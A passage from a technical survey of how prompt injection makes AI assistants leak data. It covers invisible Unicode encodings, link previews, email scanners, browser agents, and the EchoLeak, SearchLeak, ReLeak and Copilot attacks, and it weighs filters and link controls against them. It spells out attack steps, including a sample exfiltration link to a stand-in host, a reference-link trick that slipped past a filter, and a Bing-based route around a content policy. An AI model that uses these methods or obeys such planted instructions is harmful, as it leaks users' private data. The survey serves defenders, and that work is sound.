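*On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses* (Aiersilan, Yousefi and Pless, 2026) tests tag characters as a way for teachers to detect students who paste an assignment into a chatbot and hand in its answer. The tool hides an instruction in the assignment for the model to end its reply with a particular code. By the end of July 2026, each model had received four assignments, three times each.

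Claude 3 to 4, several generations of Gemini, Grok 4 Fast and the largest Qwen3 model produced the code in every trial. DeepSeek V3 and Mistral's Codestral produced it less than half the time. OpenAI's GPT-5 series never did, and Aiersilan and colleagues infer that OpenAI strips the characters from the input. Llama and the larger Mistral models never produced it either, apparently because their tokenizers did not preserve the characters.

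These results seem to contradict Graves, who found that Claude models almost never obeyed without a hint. Differences between the tasks could explain much of the gap. Graves's hidden instruction competed with the visible question, and an answer containing both the true and the hidden word did not count as obedience. The teachers' instruction only asked for something extra at the end of a normal answer, and any appearance of the code counted. Aiersilan and colleagues also based their ratings on vendors' statements and other people's reports as well as their own trials, so the ratings are less exact than Graves's percentages.

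In August 2026 tests of more recent models, Grok 4.5, Gemini 3.1 Pro and Gemini 3.6 Flash each obeyed the hidden text in all six trials. GPT-5.6 Sol ignored it, which is consistent with filtering. Claude Opus 5 showed that a model that can read tag characters can also expose them. It read the hidden text but did not follow it, and opened its reply by warning the user that the message contained hidden instructions.

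They also tested short instructions that a student might type alongside the assignment. Telling the model to disregard instructions inside the pasted text stopped nearly all of the hidden instructions from working. Forbidding extra lines or codes at the end of the answer did not help with the two larger models. Grok 4.5 still produced the code in five of six trials, and Gemini 3.1 Pro did in all six. In the web version of Grok, the displayed reasoning included the conflict between the visible and invisible instructions, followed by a decision to follow the invisible one.

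A hidden text of 256 bytes came through Gmail, Outlook, Word, Google Docs, PDF, Slack and Discord intact in at least 95 percent of trials. Posts on X and some versions of Apple Notes usually lost it. An assistant like Copilot draws mainly on email, office documents and workplace chat, so an attacker has many ways to deliver hidden text to it.

### Writing is a separate ability

In the link attack, the attacker can write the instructions in plain English, so the model does not need to read any invisible text. The model must convert the stolen data into tag characters and put them in its answer, but neither Graves nor Aiersilan and colleagues tested that.

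Hidden text is harder for a model to write than to read. A model can misread a character or two of a hidden sentence and still understand it. When it writes a login code, every digit has to be right, though a stolen email is still useful with a few errors. Writing also requires the model to produce tokens it has rarely had to produce, while reading only requires it to recognize them.

Most of the direct evidence that models can write invisible characters is older. In January 2024 Rehberger built a custom version of ChatGPT that turned whatever the user typed into tag characters and printed them between the words START and END. Anyone could paste the apparently empty space into his decoding tool and recover the text. His attack on Copilot later that year depended on the same ability. In *Sneaky Bits*, which includes experiments with ChatGPT 4.5, he writes that models can generate tag characters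 and that many also read them as instructions without help.

There is less evidence for the models of 2026. In a related test, Aiersilan and colleagues had Grok 4.5 and the two Gemini models restate an assignment that contained hidden text. None of the 18 restatements contained tag characters, so the models did not copy them by accident. But the models had not been asked to write tag characters, so the result is only weak evidence of what they would do if planted text gave them an example to imitate.

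A Python tool would probably make it much easier for the model to write tag characters, just as it made reading them easier in Graves's test, because converting text takes only a line of code. The model would still have to copy the result accurately into the link. A filter on the model's input would remove an example written in tag characters, but the model could still write new tag characters from a description in ordinary words. Removing those requires a separate filter on the output.

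### Other invisible encodings

Variation selectors can hide data too, as tag characters do. They are invisible characters that choose between forms of the character before them, such as the text and emoji versions of a symbol. There are 256 of them, so each possible value of a byte can have its own selector. *Sneaky Bits* credits Paul Butler with describing this method, and adds that the selectors apparently don't need an emoji or other visible character in front of them.

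Rehberger's own scheme, Sneaky Bits, works like zero-width binary but uses two invisible mathematical symbols, "invisible times" for 0 and "invisible plus" for 1. The letter A is 01000001 in binary, so it becomes one invisible times, one invisible plus, five more invisible times and a final invisible plus. Because the scheme works on raw bits, it can carry any data, including Chinese text and emoji. Variation selectors can too, but tag characters can spell only ASCII.

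The binary schemes need eight invisible characters for each English letter or digit. Each of those takes three bytes, or nine characters once percent-encoded:

| Encoding | Invisible characters per letter | Address characters per letter | Address characters for 481920 | Do models handle it without tools? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tag characters | 1 | 12 | 72 | Many read them, and some have written them |
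| Variation selectors | 1 | 12 | 72 | They need instructions or a tool |
| Zero-width binary | 8 | 72 | 432 | Rarely, in Graves's reading test |
| Sneaky Bits | 8 | 72 | 432 | Mixed results when writing |

The entries for zero-width binary and Sneaky Bits come from different tests, so they are not directly comparable. Rehberger's prompt for writing Sneaky Bits, which included a worked example, succeeded with ChatGPT 4.5 when the model could run code. Without tools, ChatGPT and Grok succeeded only some of the time.

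The extra length matters more for an email than for a login code. Encoding a thousand English characters would add 12,000 characters to the address with tag characters and 72,000 with either binary scheme. A longer encoding also gives the model more chances to make a mistake. A wrong tag character spoils one letter, but if the model leaves out one binary digit, everything after it shifts by one place and decodes to nonsense.

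Tag characters are therefore the most practical choice for an assistant that cannot run code, as long as the model can write them and nothing filters them out. The other encodings become more useful if a vendor filters only tag characters, or if the assistant has a code tool. None of these encodings stays hidden in Chrome's hover text, because Chromium leaves all of these characters percent-encoded.

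### The 2024 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot

Rehberger's attack on Copilot combined these techniques in a working product. In the version that stole login codes, the victim received an email with instructions for Copilot. When the victim used Copilot to work with that email, Copilot followed the instructions and searched the mailbox for confirmation codes from Slack. Embrace The Red describes the automatic search as the surprising part. Rehberger already knew that an email could manipulate Copilot's answer, but this email could also control what other private material Copilot brought into the conversation.

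The planted text then had to get Copilot to write in characters that it would hardly ever use. Rehberger included an example, since language models can often pick up a pattern from one or two examples in the prompt. In the email, the example was a link that looked ordinary but contained the phrase "hello, today is a good day" in tag characters. He instructed Copilot to write the stolen message the same way. The planted text for documents used a shorter example, the word "hello".

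The user then saw a short, clean address on Rehberger's domain, with the stolen text invisibly attached.

An attacker could also write the instructions in tag characters. Rehberger noted that the payload could include a condition that activated it only when a particular person used Copilot, so everyone else who opened the same email or document would get a normal answer.

He also described a version with a `mailto:` link, which opens a new email instead of a web page. The hidden data sits in the recipient's address, between a visible label and the @ sign. This worked in some email programs. The victim normally has to take the extra step of sending the message after clicking the link, but the data then arrives by email rather than in a web request.

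On March 14, 2024, about a month after reporting the full attack, Rehberger sent Microsoft the version that stole login codes. In April he told Microsoft that he planned to present it at the security conference HackSpaceCon. Microsoft asked for time until the end of May, and he left it out of his talk. In mid-May Microsoft was still working on what it called a comprehensive fix.

By July 2 the attack no longer worked. Microsoft reviewed a draft of Rehberger's post and, on August 22, raised no concerns. He presented the attack at the HITCON conference two days later.

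Microsoft did not explain its fix and did not respond when Rehberger asked for details that others in the industry could learn from. He had recommended that Copilot stop interpreting and displaying tag characters, stop running tools automatically, and ideally stop displaying clickable links. The only change he noticed was that Copilot no longer seemed to display links, and prompt injection still worked. Removing the links would have stopped his attack even if the model could still write tag characters, so it is hard to learn much from the fix without more details.

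### What invisibility adds

Tag characters help an attacker most when the assistant displays the link's address, as in Rehberger's attack. A login code at the end of the address could alarm the user, but if tag characters hide the code, the address seems to end after a few ordinary words and looks harmless. They also hide data from a Firefox user who hovers over a link to check it. If the API key in the Slack attack had been in tag characters, Firefox would have shown only an unfamiliar domain.

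Invisible characters add much less concealment when the link sits behind words such as "Q3 report" or "click here to reauthenticate", which already hide the entire address from anyone who doesn't hover. Slack AI and the Mermaid button both leaked data without invisible characters. Using them hides the data a little better, but the attacker has to rely on the model's ability to write unusual characters. They also make the address much longer and leave a distinctive pattern of bytes that a simple program can detect. Cisco published a detection rule that is only a few lines long.

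Invisible characters can also expose data without anyone clicking a link. Someone might copy an answer into a public document, or approve a message for sending, and pass on data they never saw. Embrace The Red raised this problem in January 2024 as a weakness of having a person review an AI system's output. Even a careful reviewer can approve the message, because the screen doesn't show all of its text.

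## When software opens the link before the user does

A link with a login code in its address sends nothing from a web chat until the user clicks it. If an assistant posts the same link in Slack, Slack's servers may open it to fetch a title and picture, giving the attacker the code before the user reads the answer. Whether an attack needs a click therefore depends on where the answer appears as well as on what the attacker planted. A finding that an attack "requires user interaction" may hold only for the interface where it was tested.

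### How a link preview sends the data

Many messaging applications show a small card with a title, description and picture under a link. To build this link preview, the application has to request the page, a step that developers call unfurling. As PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* points out, this is the same type of network request that a click produces. With the login code from the earlier example, the attack goes like this:

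1. Following the planted text, the agent writes `https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920` in its answer.
2. The agent's software posts the answer to the chat.
3. The messaging application finds the address in the message and requests the page.
4. The attacker's server logs the request, including the code.
5. The application shows a preview if the page supplied a title or picture. Otherwise the user sees only the link.

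Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* demonstrates the automatic request with a short program that posts a link to Slack. The server log recorded the visitor as "Slackbot-LinkExpanding" instead of a browser. Such a request comes from Slack's servers, so a company would not stop it by blocking the attacker's domain on its own network.

Apps generate link previews in different places. An older study, reported by SecurityWeek, found that iMessage, Signal, Viber and WhatsApp generated them on the sender's side, and Reddit's chat on the receiver's. According to a researcher quoted in TechBeacon's *Messenger apps*, Telegram's servers generated them in normal chats, downloading up to 20 MB of any file. In its encrypted "secret chats", Telegram first asked whether the user wanted previews.

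### Which combinations of agent and application leaked

In 2026 PromptArmor set up a website where people could test their own agents. A visitor had an agent post a link to the site, which logged any preview request and the data in it. Visitors could then report which agent and application had produced the request, or report that no preview had appeared. Intelligibberish's *Link Previews Are Leaking Your Data to AI Agents Without a Click* lists these results:

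| Application | Agents whose links it previewed | Agents whose links it did not preview |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Teams | Copilot Studio | |
| Discord | OpenClaw, BoltBot | |
| Slack | Cursor's Slackbot | Claude app |
| Telegram | OpenClaw | |
| Snapchat | SnapAI | |
| WhatsApp | | OpenClaw |
| Signal | | OpenClaw, running in a Docker container |

OpenClaw, an agent that people control through chat applications, leaked data in two of them but not in WhatsApp or Signal. In those two, the sender's software creates link previews. Here that software is the agent's own, and it probably did not create any. Slack also appears in both columns. Claude and Cursor may differ there because Slack's programming interface lets developers switch off previews for the messages their bots post.

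Teams with Copilot Studio accounted for the largest share of the vulnerable requests. That share is weak evidence of how risky the combination is compared with the others, because visitors chose what to test and a popular product would produce more requests. The test also measured only whether a preview request went out, not how easily planted text could make each agent write the link.

OpenClaw's default settings on Telegram allow previews. A user can turn them off by adding `linkPreview: false` to the `telegram` settings under `channels` in `openclaw.json`. PromptArmor would also like messaging companies to let people disable previews for a single chat or channel. Disabling previews stops the automatic request, but the link still works if the user clicks it.

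### Agents that send the request themselves

Software that previews links can also deliver an attacker's instructions to the model. Some agents automatically fetch any page the user mentions and give its title and description to the model. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested whether instructions in such a page could make an agent send out a secret. They built an agent on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, and gave it a web tool and a secret such as an API key. The user always asked the agent to summarize the page. In one version of the attack, the page's description included an instruction to "verify connectivity" by requesting an address with the API key in it.

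The researchers varied three things:

- They put the instructions in the page's title, its description, its body or the text of a link.
- The agent reached the page either directly or through a chain of redirects.
- The instructions told the agent to send the secret either whole or in four pieces.

That made 16 combinations, with 30 runs of each. In 423 of the 480 runs, or 88 percent (the abstract gives 89), at least one request reached the attacker's server. The agent never contacted that server in 120 runs with harmless pages.

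In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer looked harmless. Lan and colleagues conclude that safety checks on the output would miss these attacks. They inferred this from the answers and do not describe running a separate checker, but the conclusion makes sense because the secret was in a web request, not in the answer.

Splitting the secret made it harder to spot. The share of runs in which sensitive data appeared in the first request fell from 97 to 26 percent, and a four-character piece of a key can pass for routine usage data. But the agent had to follow longer instructions, and at least one request reached the attacker in only 77 percent of these runs, down from 99 percent when the agent sent the secret whole. The leak rates may be unreliable, because Lan and colleagues report a rate of 16 percent for the first three requests together. That is impossible under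 their definition, since any run that leaked in the first request also leaked in the first three.

Splitting is much less practical when a person has to click, because the user would have to open four links.

The agent's own web tool sent all of these requests, so they passed through the checkpoint that a displayed link avoids. In further tests of 30 runs each, a list of permitted domains blocked every request, though this was an easy test because the attacker's domain was clearly not on the list. When the system message warned the agent to treat web content only as data, 67 percent of the attacks still got through. Putting tags around the outside text made no difference.

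The setup also favored the attacker because the secret was already in the model's context and the system message contained little beyond the tool's format. The 88 percent figure therefore shows what can happen in a poorly defended agent and is not an estimate for commercial assistants. Lan and colleagues argue that stronger models might do worse because they follow instructions more reliably, but tested only one model.

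### Assistants that control a browser

If an assistant built into a browser can open pages without asking, data can be stolen through a link that the user never clicks. When planted text makes the assistant navigate to an address, the browser sends the data as it opens that address. The user still has to click if the assistant only summarizes a page and displays a link.

Willison describes an attack of this kind that PromptArmor demonstrated in 2025 on Google Antigravity, a programming environment whose agent can use a browser. A web page disguised as a technical guide got the agent to collect passwords and code from the user's workspace and send them out through the browser. Antigravity restricted which sites the browser could visit, but its default list of allowed sites included webhook.site, a service where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it.

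Anthropic restricts Claude's fetch tool by exact address instead of by domain. The tool opens only addresses that the user typed or that Claude's search tool returned. However, Willison (2026) reports that Ayush Paul found a flaw in this design in July.

### Email link scanners

Many companies use security products that check the links in incoming email. Some compare each address with a list of known malicious sites, which sends nothing to the attacker. Others open the page to look for malware or a fake login form. If the address contains stolen data, opening the page sends that data to the attacker, even if the scanner then blocks the page.

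These scanners do not normally check answers in a web chat, but they matter when the assistant's text is emailed, for instance when an agent sends a daily summary or the user forwards an answer to a colleague. A scanner that opens links on delivery sends the data before the recipient reads the message, so no click is needed. If the scanner waits for a click, a person still triggers the request, but a warning page may appear only after the scanner has sent the data.

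### Clicks that lead into the assistant

In some "one-click" attacks, the user clicks before the assistant has done anything. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that began with a link in an email or chat message. The link led to Copilot's real search page and contained a search query after `q=`. Copilot treated the query as instructions and followed them as soon as the page opened.

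The instructions told Copilot to find an email and put its title in the address of an image. Three things then happened without another click:

1. The browser loaded the image while Copilot was still writing. Microsoft's software made HTML in answers harmless, but only after the answer was complete.
2. The page's Content Security Policy would have blocked an image from the attacker's server, but it allowed images from bing.com. The image address therefore pointed to Bing's search-by-image feature and included the attacker's address as the picture to look up.
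3. Bing's server requested that picture, and the attacker's log recorded a path such as `/Your_Security_Code_847291/img.png`.

In the Microsoft 365 Copilot attack, the user's click delivered the instructions, and the data then left automatically. This makes the attack hard to classify. When scoring its severity, Microsoft counted it as needing user interaction, but the US National Vulnerability Database did not, according to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026).

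A user who inspects the link will find different clues in each kind of attack. In the Slack AI attack, the address contained the stolen key and an unfamiliar domain. A SearchLeak link led to a genuine Microsoft site and contained no private data, because Copilot had not yet searched for any. The only clue was a long query containing instructions.

*Reprompt* (Taler, 2026) describes another attack that started the same way as SearchLeak. It needed one click on a legitimate Microsoft link and targeted the consumer version of Copilot. Microsoft has also found many real attempts to use links with ready-made prompts, though these tried to plant lasting recommendations in the assistant's memory rather than steal data. Microsoft lists URL formats for such links for Copilot, ChatGPT, Claude, Perplexity and Grok.

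### What the ReLeak attacks used

The three ReLeak attacks that Simonovich disclosed in December 2026 did not need a click at either end. The attacker sent an email, which the victim did not have to open, and Copilot read it while handling an ordinary work request. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, and Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, describe the same three routes:

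- **An image fetched through Bing.** The browser loaded an image from Copilot's answer, and Bing passed the data to the attacker's server. Varonis had announced in June that Microsoft had patched SearchLeak, which used a similar route, but Cato did not begin reporting the ReLeak flaws until July 29. The earlier patch had apparently left another way to use Bing.
- **A link in a file.** Copilot saved a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with private data in its address. Microsoft's servers opened the link during background processing, between one and eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody opened the file.
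- **The code interpreter.** Copilot can run Python code in an environment that, according to Microsoft's documentation, has no network access. The researchers got around this restriction and sent the data directly.

Of the three attacks, the file attack is the most similar to what happens when an email scanner opens a link. A link in a document normally opens only when a reader clicks it, but here Microsoft's software opened it first.

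The Bing route also resembles EchoLeak, a zero-click attack on Copilot that the same team disclosed in June 2025. Reddy and Gujral (2025) explain in *EchoLeak* that the attack used an automatically loaded image and a Microsoft Teams proxy, a server that fetches content for the browser. Copilot's Content Security Policy allowed the proxy, just as it later allowed Bing in SearchLeak. The policy controlled which server the browser contacted, but not where that server sent its own request.

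### When a confirmation comes too late

Some assistants could ask the user to confirm before opening an unfamiliar link. Such a dialog protects the data only if nothing has opened the address already:

| What requests the address | When | Can a dialog at the click prevent it? |
|---|---|---|
| The user's browser, from a link in a web chat | When the user clicks | Yes |
| A messaging application building a preview | When the agent posts the answer | No |
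| An email scanner | On delivery or at the click, depending on the product | Not if it scans on delivery |
| An agent's web or browser tool | While the agent works | No |
| The user's browser, loading an image | While the answer appears | No |
| Microsoft's servers, processing a file in ReLeak | One to eight minutes after the conversation | No |

To prevent leaks through link previews, either the link must be checked before the agent posts its answer, or the messaging application must not fetch it. The assistant's maker may control only the check, since its customers can connect the same agent to Teams, Slack or Telegram. If a preview has already fetched the link, a user who sees the warning and clicks "Cancel" will think they have prevented a leak, although the login code is already in the attacker's log.

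## Removing invisible characters from text and links

People cannot see tag characters, but software can find them easily because they all lie between U+E0000 and U+E007F. A filter can delete them from the text an assistant reads, from its answers and from the addresses of its links. This stops attackers from using them to hide text, but a link can still carry stolen data in ordinary letters and digits.

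### How the filter works

A filter that spares the legitimate flag emoji could work like this:

1. Decode the text into code points.
2. Find every code point from U+E0000 to U+E007F.
3. Keep those that belong to the flags of England, Scotland and Wales, which consist of a black flag, the tag letters "gbeng", "gbsct" or "gbwls", and a closing tag.
4. Delete the others, or block the message and raise an alert.
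5. Repeat until a pass changes nothing.

Step 3 needs an exact match, because a black flag followed by other tag letters could carry stolen data. Counting the tag characters is not enough, because England's flag contains six, the same number as the hidden login code 481920. The scanner in Embrace The Red's *Scary Agent Skills* rates a run of tag characters as high severity only when it is longer than ten. That limit suits the scanner's purpose of finding hidden instructions, but a six-digit code would stay under it.

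The reason for step 5 is a flaw that AWS's *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling* found in a commonly proposed filter for the programming language Java. Java stores text in 16-bit units, which are too small for a tag character's number. It therefore splits the character into two units, called a high surrogate and a low surrogate. The tag character U+E0001, for example, becomes DB40 followed by DC01. An attacker can wrap one such pair inside another:

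| Stage | Stored units | How Java reads them |
|---|---|---|
| Attacker's text | DB40 DB40 DC01 DC01 | A stray half, a tag character, a stray half |
| After one pass | DB40 DC01 | A tag character |
| After a second pass | None | Nothing |

The first pass deletes the tag character between two stray surrogates (halves of an encoded character), which then join to form a new tag character. AWS's corrected code repeats until the text stops changing and also deletes stray surrogates. Python does not join surrogates in this way, so one pass is enough there.

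This kind of code is easy to get slightly wrong. AWS's corrected Java version looks for stray surrogates using only the last 16 bits of each code point, so it also deletes some rare Chinese characters. AWS separately offers two rules for its Bedrock service that block prompts and answers containing tag characters instead of cleaning them. The sample surrogate pairs for one of those rules, such as `\uDB40\uDD41`, encode variation selectors rather than tag characters.

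### Where the filter has to run

A filter on the model's input has to cover everything the model reads, including emails, calendar entries and the results of tool calls. Embrace The Red's *Google Jules is Vulnerable To Invisible Prompt Injection* describes how Jules, Google's coding agent, copied the text of a GitHub issue, including its invisible instructions, into its task. Jules then added the attacker's function to the code and ran it. Graves argues that filtering at the tokenizer would be most robust, because the model would then never receive hidden text from any source.

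Embrace The Red's *Amp Code* describes an attack on Amp, Sourcegraph's coding agent. Invisible instructions got Amp to find a secret on the user's machine, put it in a URL's query string and send it by opening the page or loading an image. Sourcegraph fixed this by filtering invisible characters out of Amp's input. The same filter on Amp's output would have found nothing, because the secret was in ordinary characters.

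In Rehberger's 2024 attack on Copilot, the instructions were in plain English and the stolen text was in invisible tag characters. A filter that removed tag characters from the output would have deleted the stolen text before Copilot displayed the link.

An output filter can miss hidden data if the model writes the invisible characters as percent codes. The tag character for the digit 4, for example, becomes `%F3%A0%80%B4`, which contains only ordinary characters. The filter therefore has to percent-decode a copy of each address in the answer and search that copy. An attacker could encode the percent signs as well, giving `%25F3%25A0%2580%25B4`, so the filter should repeat the decoding until nothing changes. If it finds a tag character, blocking the link is safer than removing the character, because the rest of the address still leads to the attacker's server.

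| Where the filter runs | What it stops | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Content entering the model | Instructions and examples written in tag characters | Instructions in ordinary text, including white text on white |
| The model's answer | Stolen data written in tag characters, in a link or in text the user might copy | Tag characters written as percent codes |
| Link addresses, after percent-decoding | Tag characters written as percent codes | Data in ordinary letters and digits |

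### False alarms in Microsoft's email

Deleting every tag character does little harm. AWS warns that the flags of England, Scotland and Wales will reach the model as plain black flags, but this rarely matters to a business. Raising an alert for every tag character causes more trouble. In *ASCII smuggling crosses over from AI prompt injection to phishing evasion*, Kochavi and Wolstencroft (2026) describe searching email for hidden instructions to AI systems. Their first detector matched any tag character and kept catching legitimate messages, all of which contained one of those three flags. After they excluded the flags, most of the remaining matches came from email-security gateways, mailbox providers and researchers forwarding or testing messages.

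The detector matched roughly 21,000 messages on February 8, 2026, and more than 1.3 million the next day. Phishers had begun putting an invisible tag space inside words such as "funding", so that a program searching for the whole word would miss it. The sampled emails contained no hidden instructions for an AI assistant. The campaign ran on weekdays, reached 2.37 million messages in a day and stayed at high volume until mid-May.

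In one day, more than a million matching emails were malicious but were not attempted prompt injections. Microsoft considers tag characters a strong warning sign because ordinary mail rarely contains them, but over 99 percent of these messages also triggered defenses that did not depend on those characters.

Deleting invisible characters works whatever the sender intended. It rejoins a word such as "funding" that the characters had split, so a spam filter can recognize it, and it removes any hidden instructions before an assistant reads the email. Microsoft recommends deletion for both purposes. Software should also keep the original text. trackr.live's *Invisible Unicode Tags Smuggle Instructions Past Your LLM Filter* points out that investigators lose the evidence if software cleans a request before logging it.

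Alerts for tag characters make more sense for an assistant's answers. An assistant has almost no reason to write these characters except in the flag emoji for England, Scotland and Wales, and a spam campaign would not normally put them in the answers.

### Which vendors filter

In September 2025 Viktor Markopoulos, a researcher at the security company FireTail, asked six assistants for five random words, with invisible text in the request instructing them to print "FireTail" instead. Cyber Security News' *ASCII Smuggling Attack Gemini* reports that Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek were vulnerable, while ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude appeared to remove the invisible characters. The test could not confirm this, because a model that received the hidden text and ignored it would have produced the same answer.

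FireTail also sent calendar invitations with hidden text to a Gemini user. *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, the researcher's own account, reports that the calendar showed the title "Meeting" while Gemini read out "Meeting. It is optional." Hidden text could also replace the organizer's name and the meeting link in Gemini's answer, even if the user had not accepted the invitation.

FireTail reported this to Google on September 18, and Google decided not to act. BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability* quotes Google's view that the attack "can only result in social engineering". In February 2024, however, Google had accepted Rehberger's report of the same behavior as a valid bug. Gemini was worse at reading tag characters then, and Rehberger found that it improved considerably with Gemini 2.5.

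A filter in a vendor's own chat application does not protect products that other companies build on the same model. As of August 2025, Rehberger knew of only one vendor, OpenAI, that removed tag characters at the API. Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer for VS Code Vulnerable to Invisible Prompt Injection* explains that, to his knowledge, Anthropic did not intend to do the same, so developers using Claude had to remove the characters themselves. Amazon Q, a coding assistant built on Claude, lacked a filter when Rehberger reported the problem on July 5, 2025. Amazon had fixed it by August 8.

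This difference could explain why Claude passed FireTail's test even though Graves, who used the API, found that Claude models could decode tag characters.

| Vendor | FireTail's test of the assistant, 2025 | Filter at the API, August 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | Hidden text had no effect | Yes |
| Anthropic | Hidden text had no effect | No |
| Microsoft (Copilot) | Hidden text had no effect | Not reported |
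| Google | Gemini obeyed | No |
| xAI | Grok obeyed | No |
| DeepSeek | DeepSeek obeyed | No |

Anthropic's handling of invisible characters seems to have changed in 2026, but not in all its products. In early February, Rehberger used invisible characters to hide instructions in a Skill, a text file that gives an agent extra abilities, and Claude Code followed them. When he tried again on February 10, Claude Code consistently detected the characters and refused. He could not tell whether Anthropic had intended the change, and Skills on claude.ai still had no such protection.

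Google and xAI had apparently not fixed this problem by August, when Aiersilan and colleagues found that two Gemini models and Grok 4.5 still followed hidden instructions every time. Developers who use these models therefore need their own filter, and should retest it when they change models.

### Other invisible characters

A filter that removes only tag characters misses other invisible characters. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025) tested 235 Unicode control and format characters in a terminal, a text document and a CSV file, and 130 left no visible trace. Unicode has 97 tag characters, so at least 33 of those 130 were not tag characters. A binary scheme such as Sneaky Bits needs only two invisible characters. The test did not include variation selectors, which belong to another Unicode category.

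FireTail's *Peek-A-Boo! 🫣 Emoji Smuggling and Modern LLMs* (2026) describes a test that January that hid text in variation selectors attached to an emoji. The attack worked on Gemini and, at the second attempt, on Grok, but failed on ChatGPT, Claude, DeepSeek and Meta's assistant. Gemini could not decode the text unaided, so the visible part of the prompt had to explain the method, which makes the attack easier to notice than one with tag characters.

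Deleting every invisible character would damage ordinary text. Graves warns that some Indic scripts and emoji made of several symbols, such as families, need zero-width joiners. Ordinary emoji also use variation selectors, and Arabic and Hebrew text can need direction marks. Graves therefore recommends looking for the patterns that encoding schemes produce instead of banning whole categories of characters. For example, a long run of variation selectors is suspicious because normal text uses one at a time. An attacker could respond by spreading the characters out among visible letters.

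Removing a list of characters can damage ordinary text and still miss characters used in attacks. The sanitizer in *enclawed* (2026), a security framework for AI assistants, removes zero-width joiners, which breaks up combined emoji, but its listed steps do not cover tag characters or the two symbols that Sneaky Bits uses.

Broader filters catch more. *Antares-Smaug* (2026) compared a filter built from known attacks with one that removes all format characters, variation selectors and several other kinds. Against Unicode tricks that the narrow filter's designers had not planned for, the narrow filter reduced the attacks' effect by about a third and the broad filter by about 95 percent. The researchers had those tricks in mind when they wrote the broad filter, so it might do worse against new ones. Developers can test their own filters with *Ascii Smuggling*, a part of the open-source testing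 tool garak that generates hidden text in tag characters, variation selectors and Sneaky Bits.

A filter that also replaces visible look-alikes, such as a Cyrillic letter that resembles a Latin "a", alters more legitimate text. *Attacking Only Half the Data* (2026), a study of software that detects AI-written text, found that removing inserted zero-width characters restored 97 percent of documents exactly. However, applying Unicode's full list of look-alikes changed 15 percent of documents that nobody had tampered with, compared with 3 percent for a hand-picked list of 47 pairs.

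A filter can be stricter with addresses than with prose, since few addresses need invisible characters. But many Persian Wikipedia page addresses contain zero-width non-joiners, so a rule that blocked every link containing one would also block links to those pages.

Even a perfect filter would leave this address unchanged:

`https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920`

A link can carry a login code as six ordinary digits, and a filter cannot delete digits from addresses without breaking much of the web. Removing invisible characters would not have stopped the Slack AI or Mermaid attacks, which used none. If a filter removes an attacker's hidden text, the attacker can switch to visible characters by changing a sentence or two of the planted instructions.

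## Blocking, redacting and rewriting links when an answer is displayed

Software cannot reliably tell a stolen login code from any other digits in an address. It can restrict the link itself, because the application that displays the answer decides whether the model's Markdown becomes something the user can click. Suppose the model writes `[Q3 report](https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920)`, where 481920 is the stolen code. Five controls, from strictest to loosest, would treat that link as follows:

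| Control | What the software examines | When it permits a link | What the user sees | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No clickable links | Every link | Never | The words "Q3 report" | Link formats that the software misses |
| Addresses as plain text | Every link | Never | "Q3 report" and the full address, which does nothing when clicked | The user can paste the address into a browser |
| Domain allow-list | The host name | If the host is on the list | The words "Q3 report" | Listed sites that store or forward data for outsiders |
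| Reputation check | The address, against known threats | Unless it matches a threat | A working link, if the domain is new | New domains |
| Redirect page | The host name | Always, but through the vendor's page | A link that first opens a confirmation page | Exempt domains, and users who continue |

Vendors combine these controls with other defenses. Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defenses, such as a classifier that looks for injected instructions, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails whatever the model does. It lists Markdown images and "certain untrusted links" among the routes it blocks deterministically, but does not say which links it considers untrusted. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes a sanitizer that stops Gemini from displaying external images and a reputation check that removes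 suspicious links.

### Removing every link

The strictest control is to remove the address from every link in the answer, regardless of where it leads, and keep only the link's text. Microsoft seems to have done something like this when it fixed Rehberger's 2024 attack, and it later removed clickable links from Copilot's diagrams.

Telling the model not to write links cannot replace filtering them at display, as a similar attempt with images showed. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) describes the assistant in Colab, Google's online tool for writing and running code in notebooks. The assistant's system message included an instruction not to display images. In November 2023 Rehberger asked the assistant to join fragments such as `![t`, `](htt` and `ps`, which formed an image only when combined. The model complied, and the image's address carried the previous chat message to his server.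 Google fixed the flaw.

### How EchoLeak got a link past the filter

To remove every link, software first has to find every link, and Markdown has several ways to write one. The usual inline form puts the address in parentheses after the words. The reference form puts a label there and gives the address elsewhere:

```
See [this document][ref].

[ref]: https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920
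```

Inline and reference links both appear on screen as ordinary clickable words. Reddy and Gujral explain that Copilot's filter removed external links in the inline form but missed those in the reference form, which the display software accepted. The EchoLeak email therefore instructed Copilot to write a reference link, which reached the user. This attack still required a click, but the researchers who reported the flaw removed that requirement by using an image in the same reference form. They reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025, and Microsoft deployed the full fix in May.

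EchoLeak worked because the filter and the display read the same text by different rules. Any link format that the display accepts and the filter does not recognize will get through. Raw HTML may be another such format. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* notes that the image in the SearchLeak attack was an HTML tag. Many applications also turn a bare web address into a link.

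The general fix is to apply the rule after parsing. A Markdown parser converts text into a tree of elements, such as paragraphs, images and links. Inline links and reference links produce the same kind of element, so software that checks the tree just before display examines the same links that the user could click. The check must also cover links that a step after parsing adds, such as those made from bare addresses.

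Reddy and Gujral also report that Microsoft began removing reference-style links and images from outside content before Copilot reads it, so that the model has no example of the format to copy there. But planted text can still describe the format in words, so the output must be checked too.

### Showing addresses as plain text

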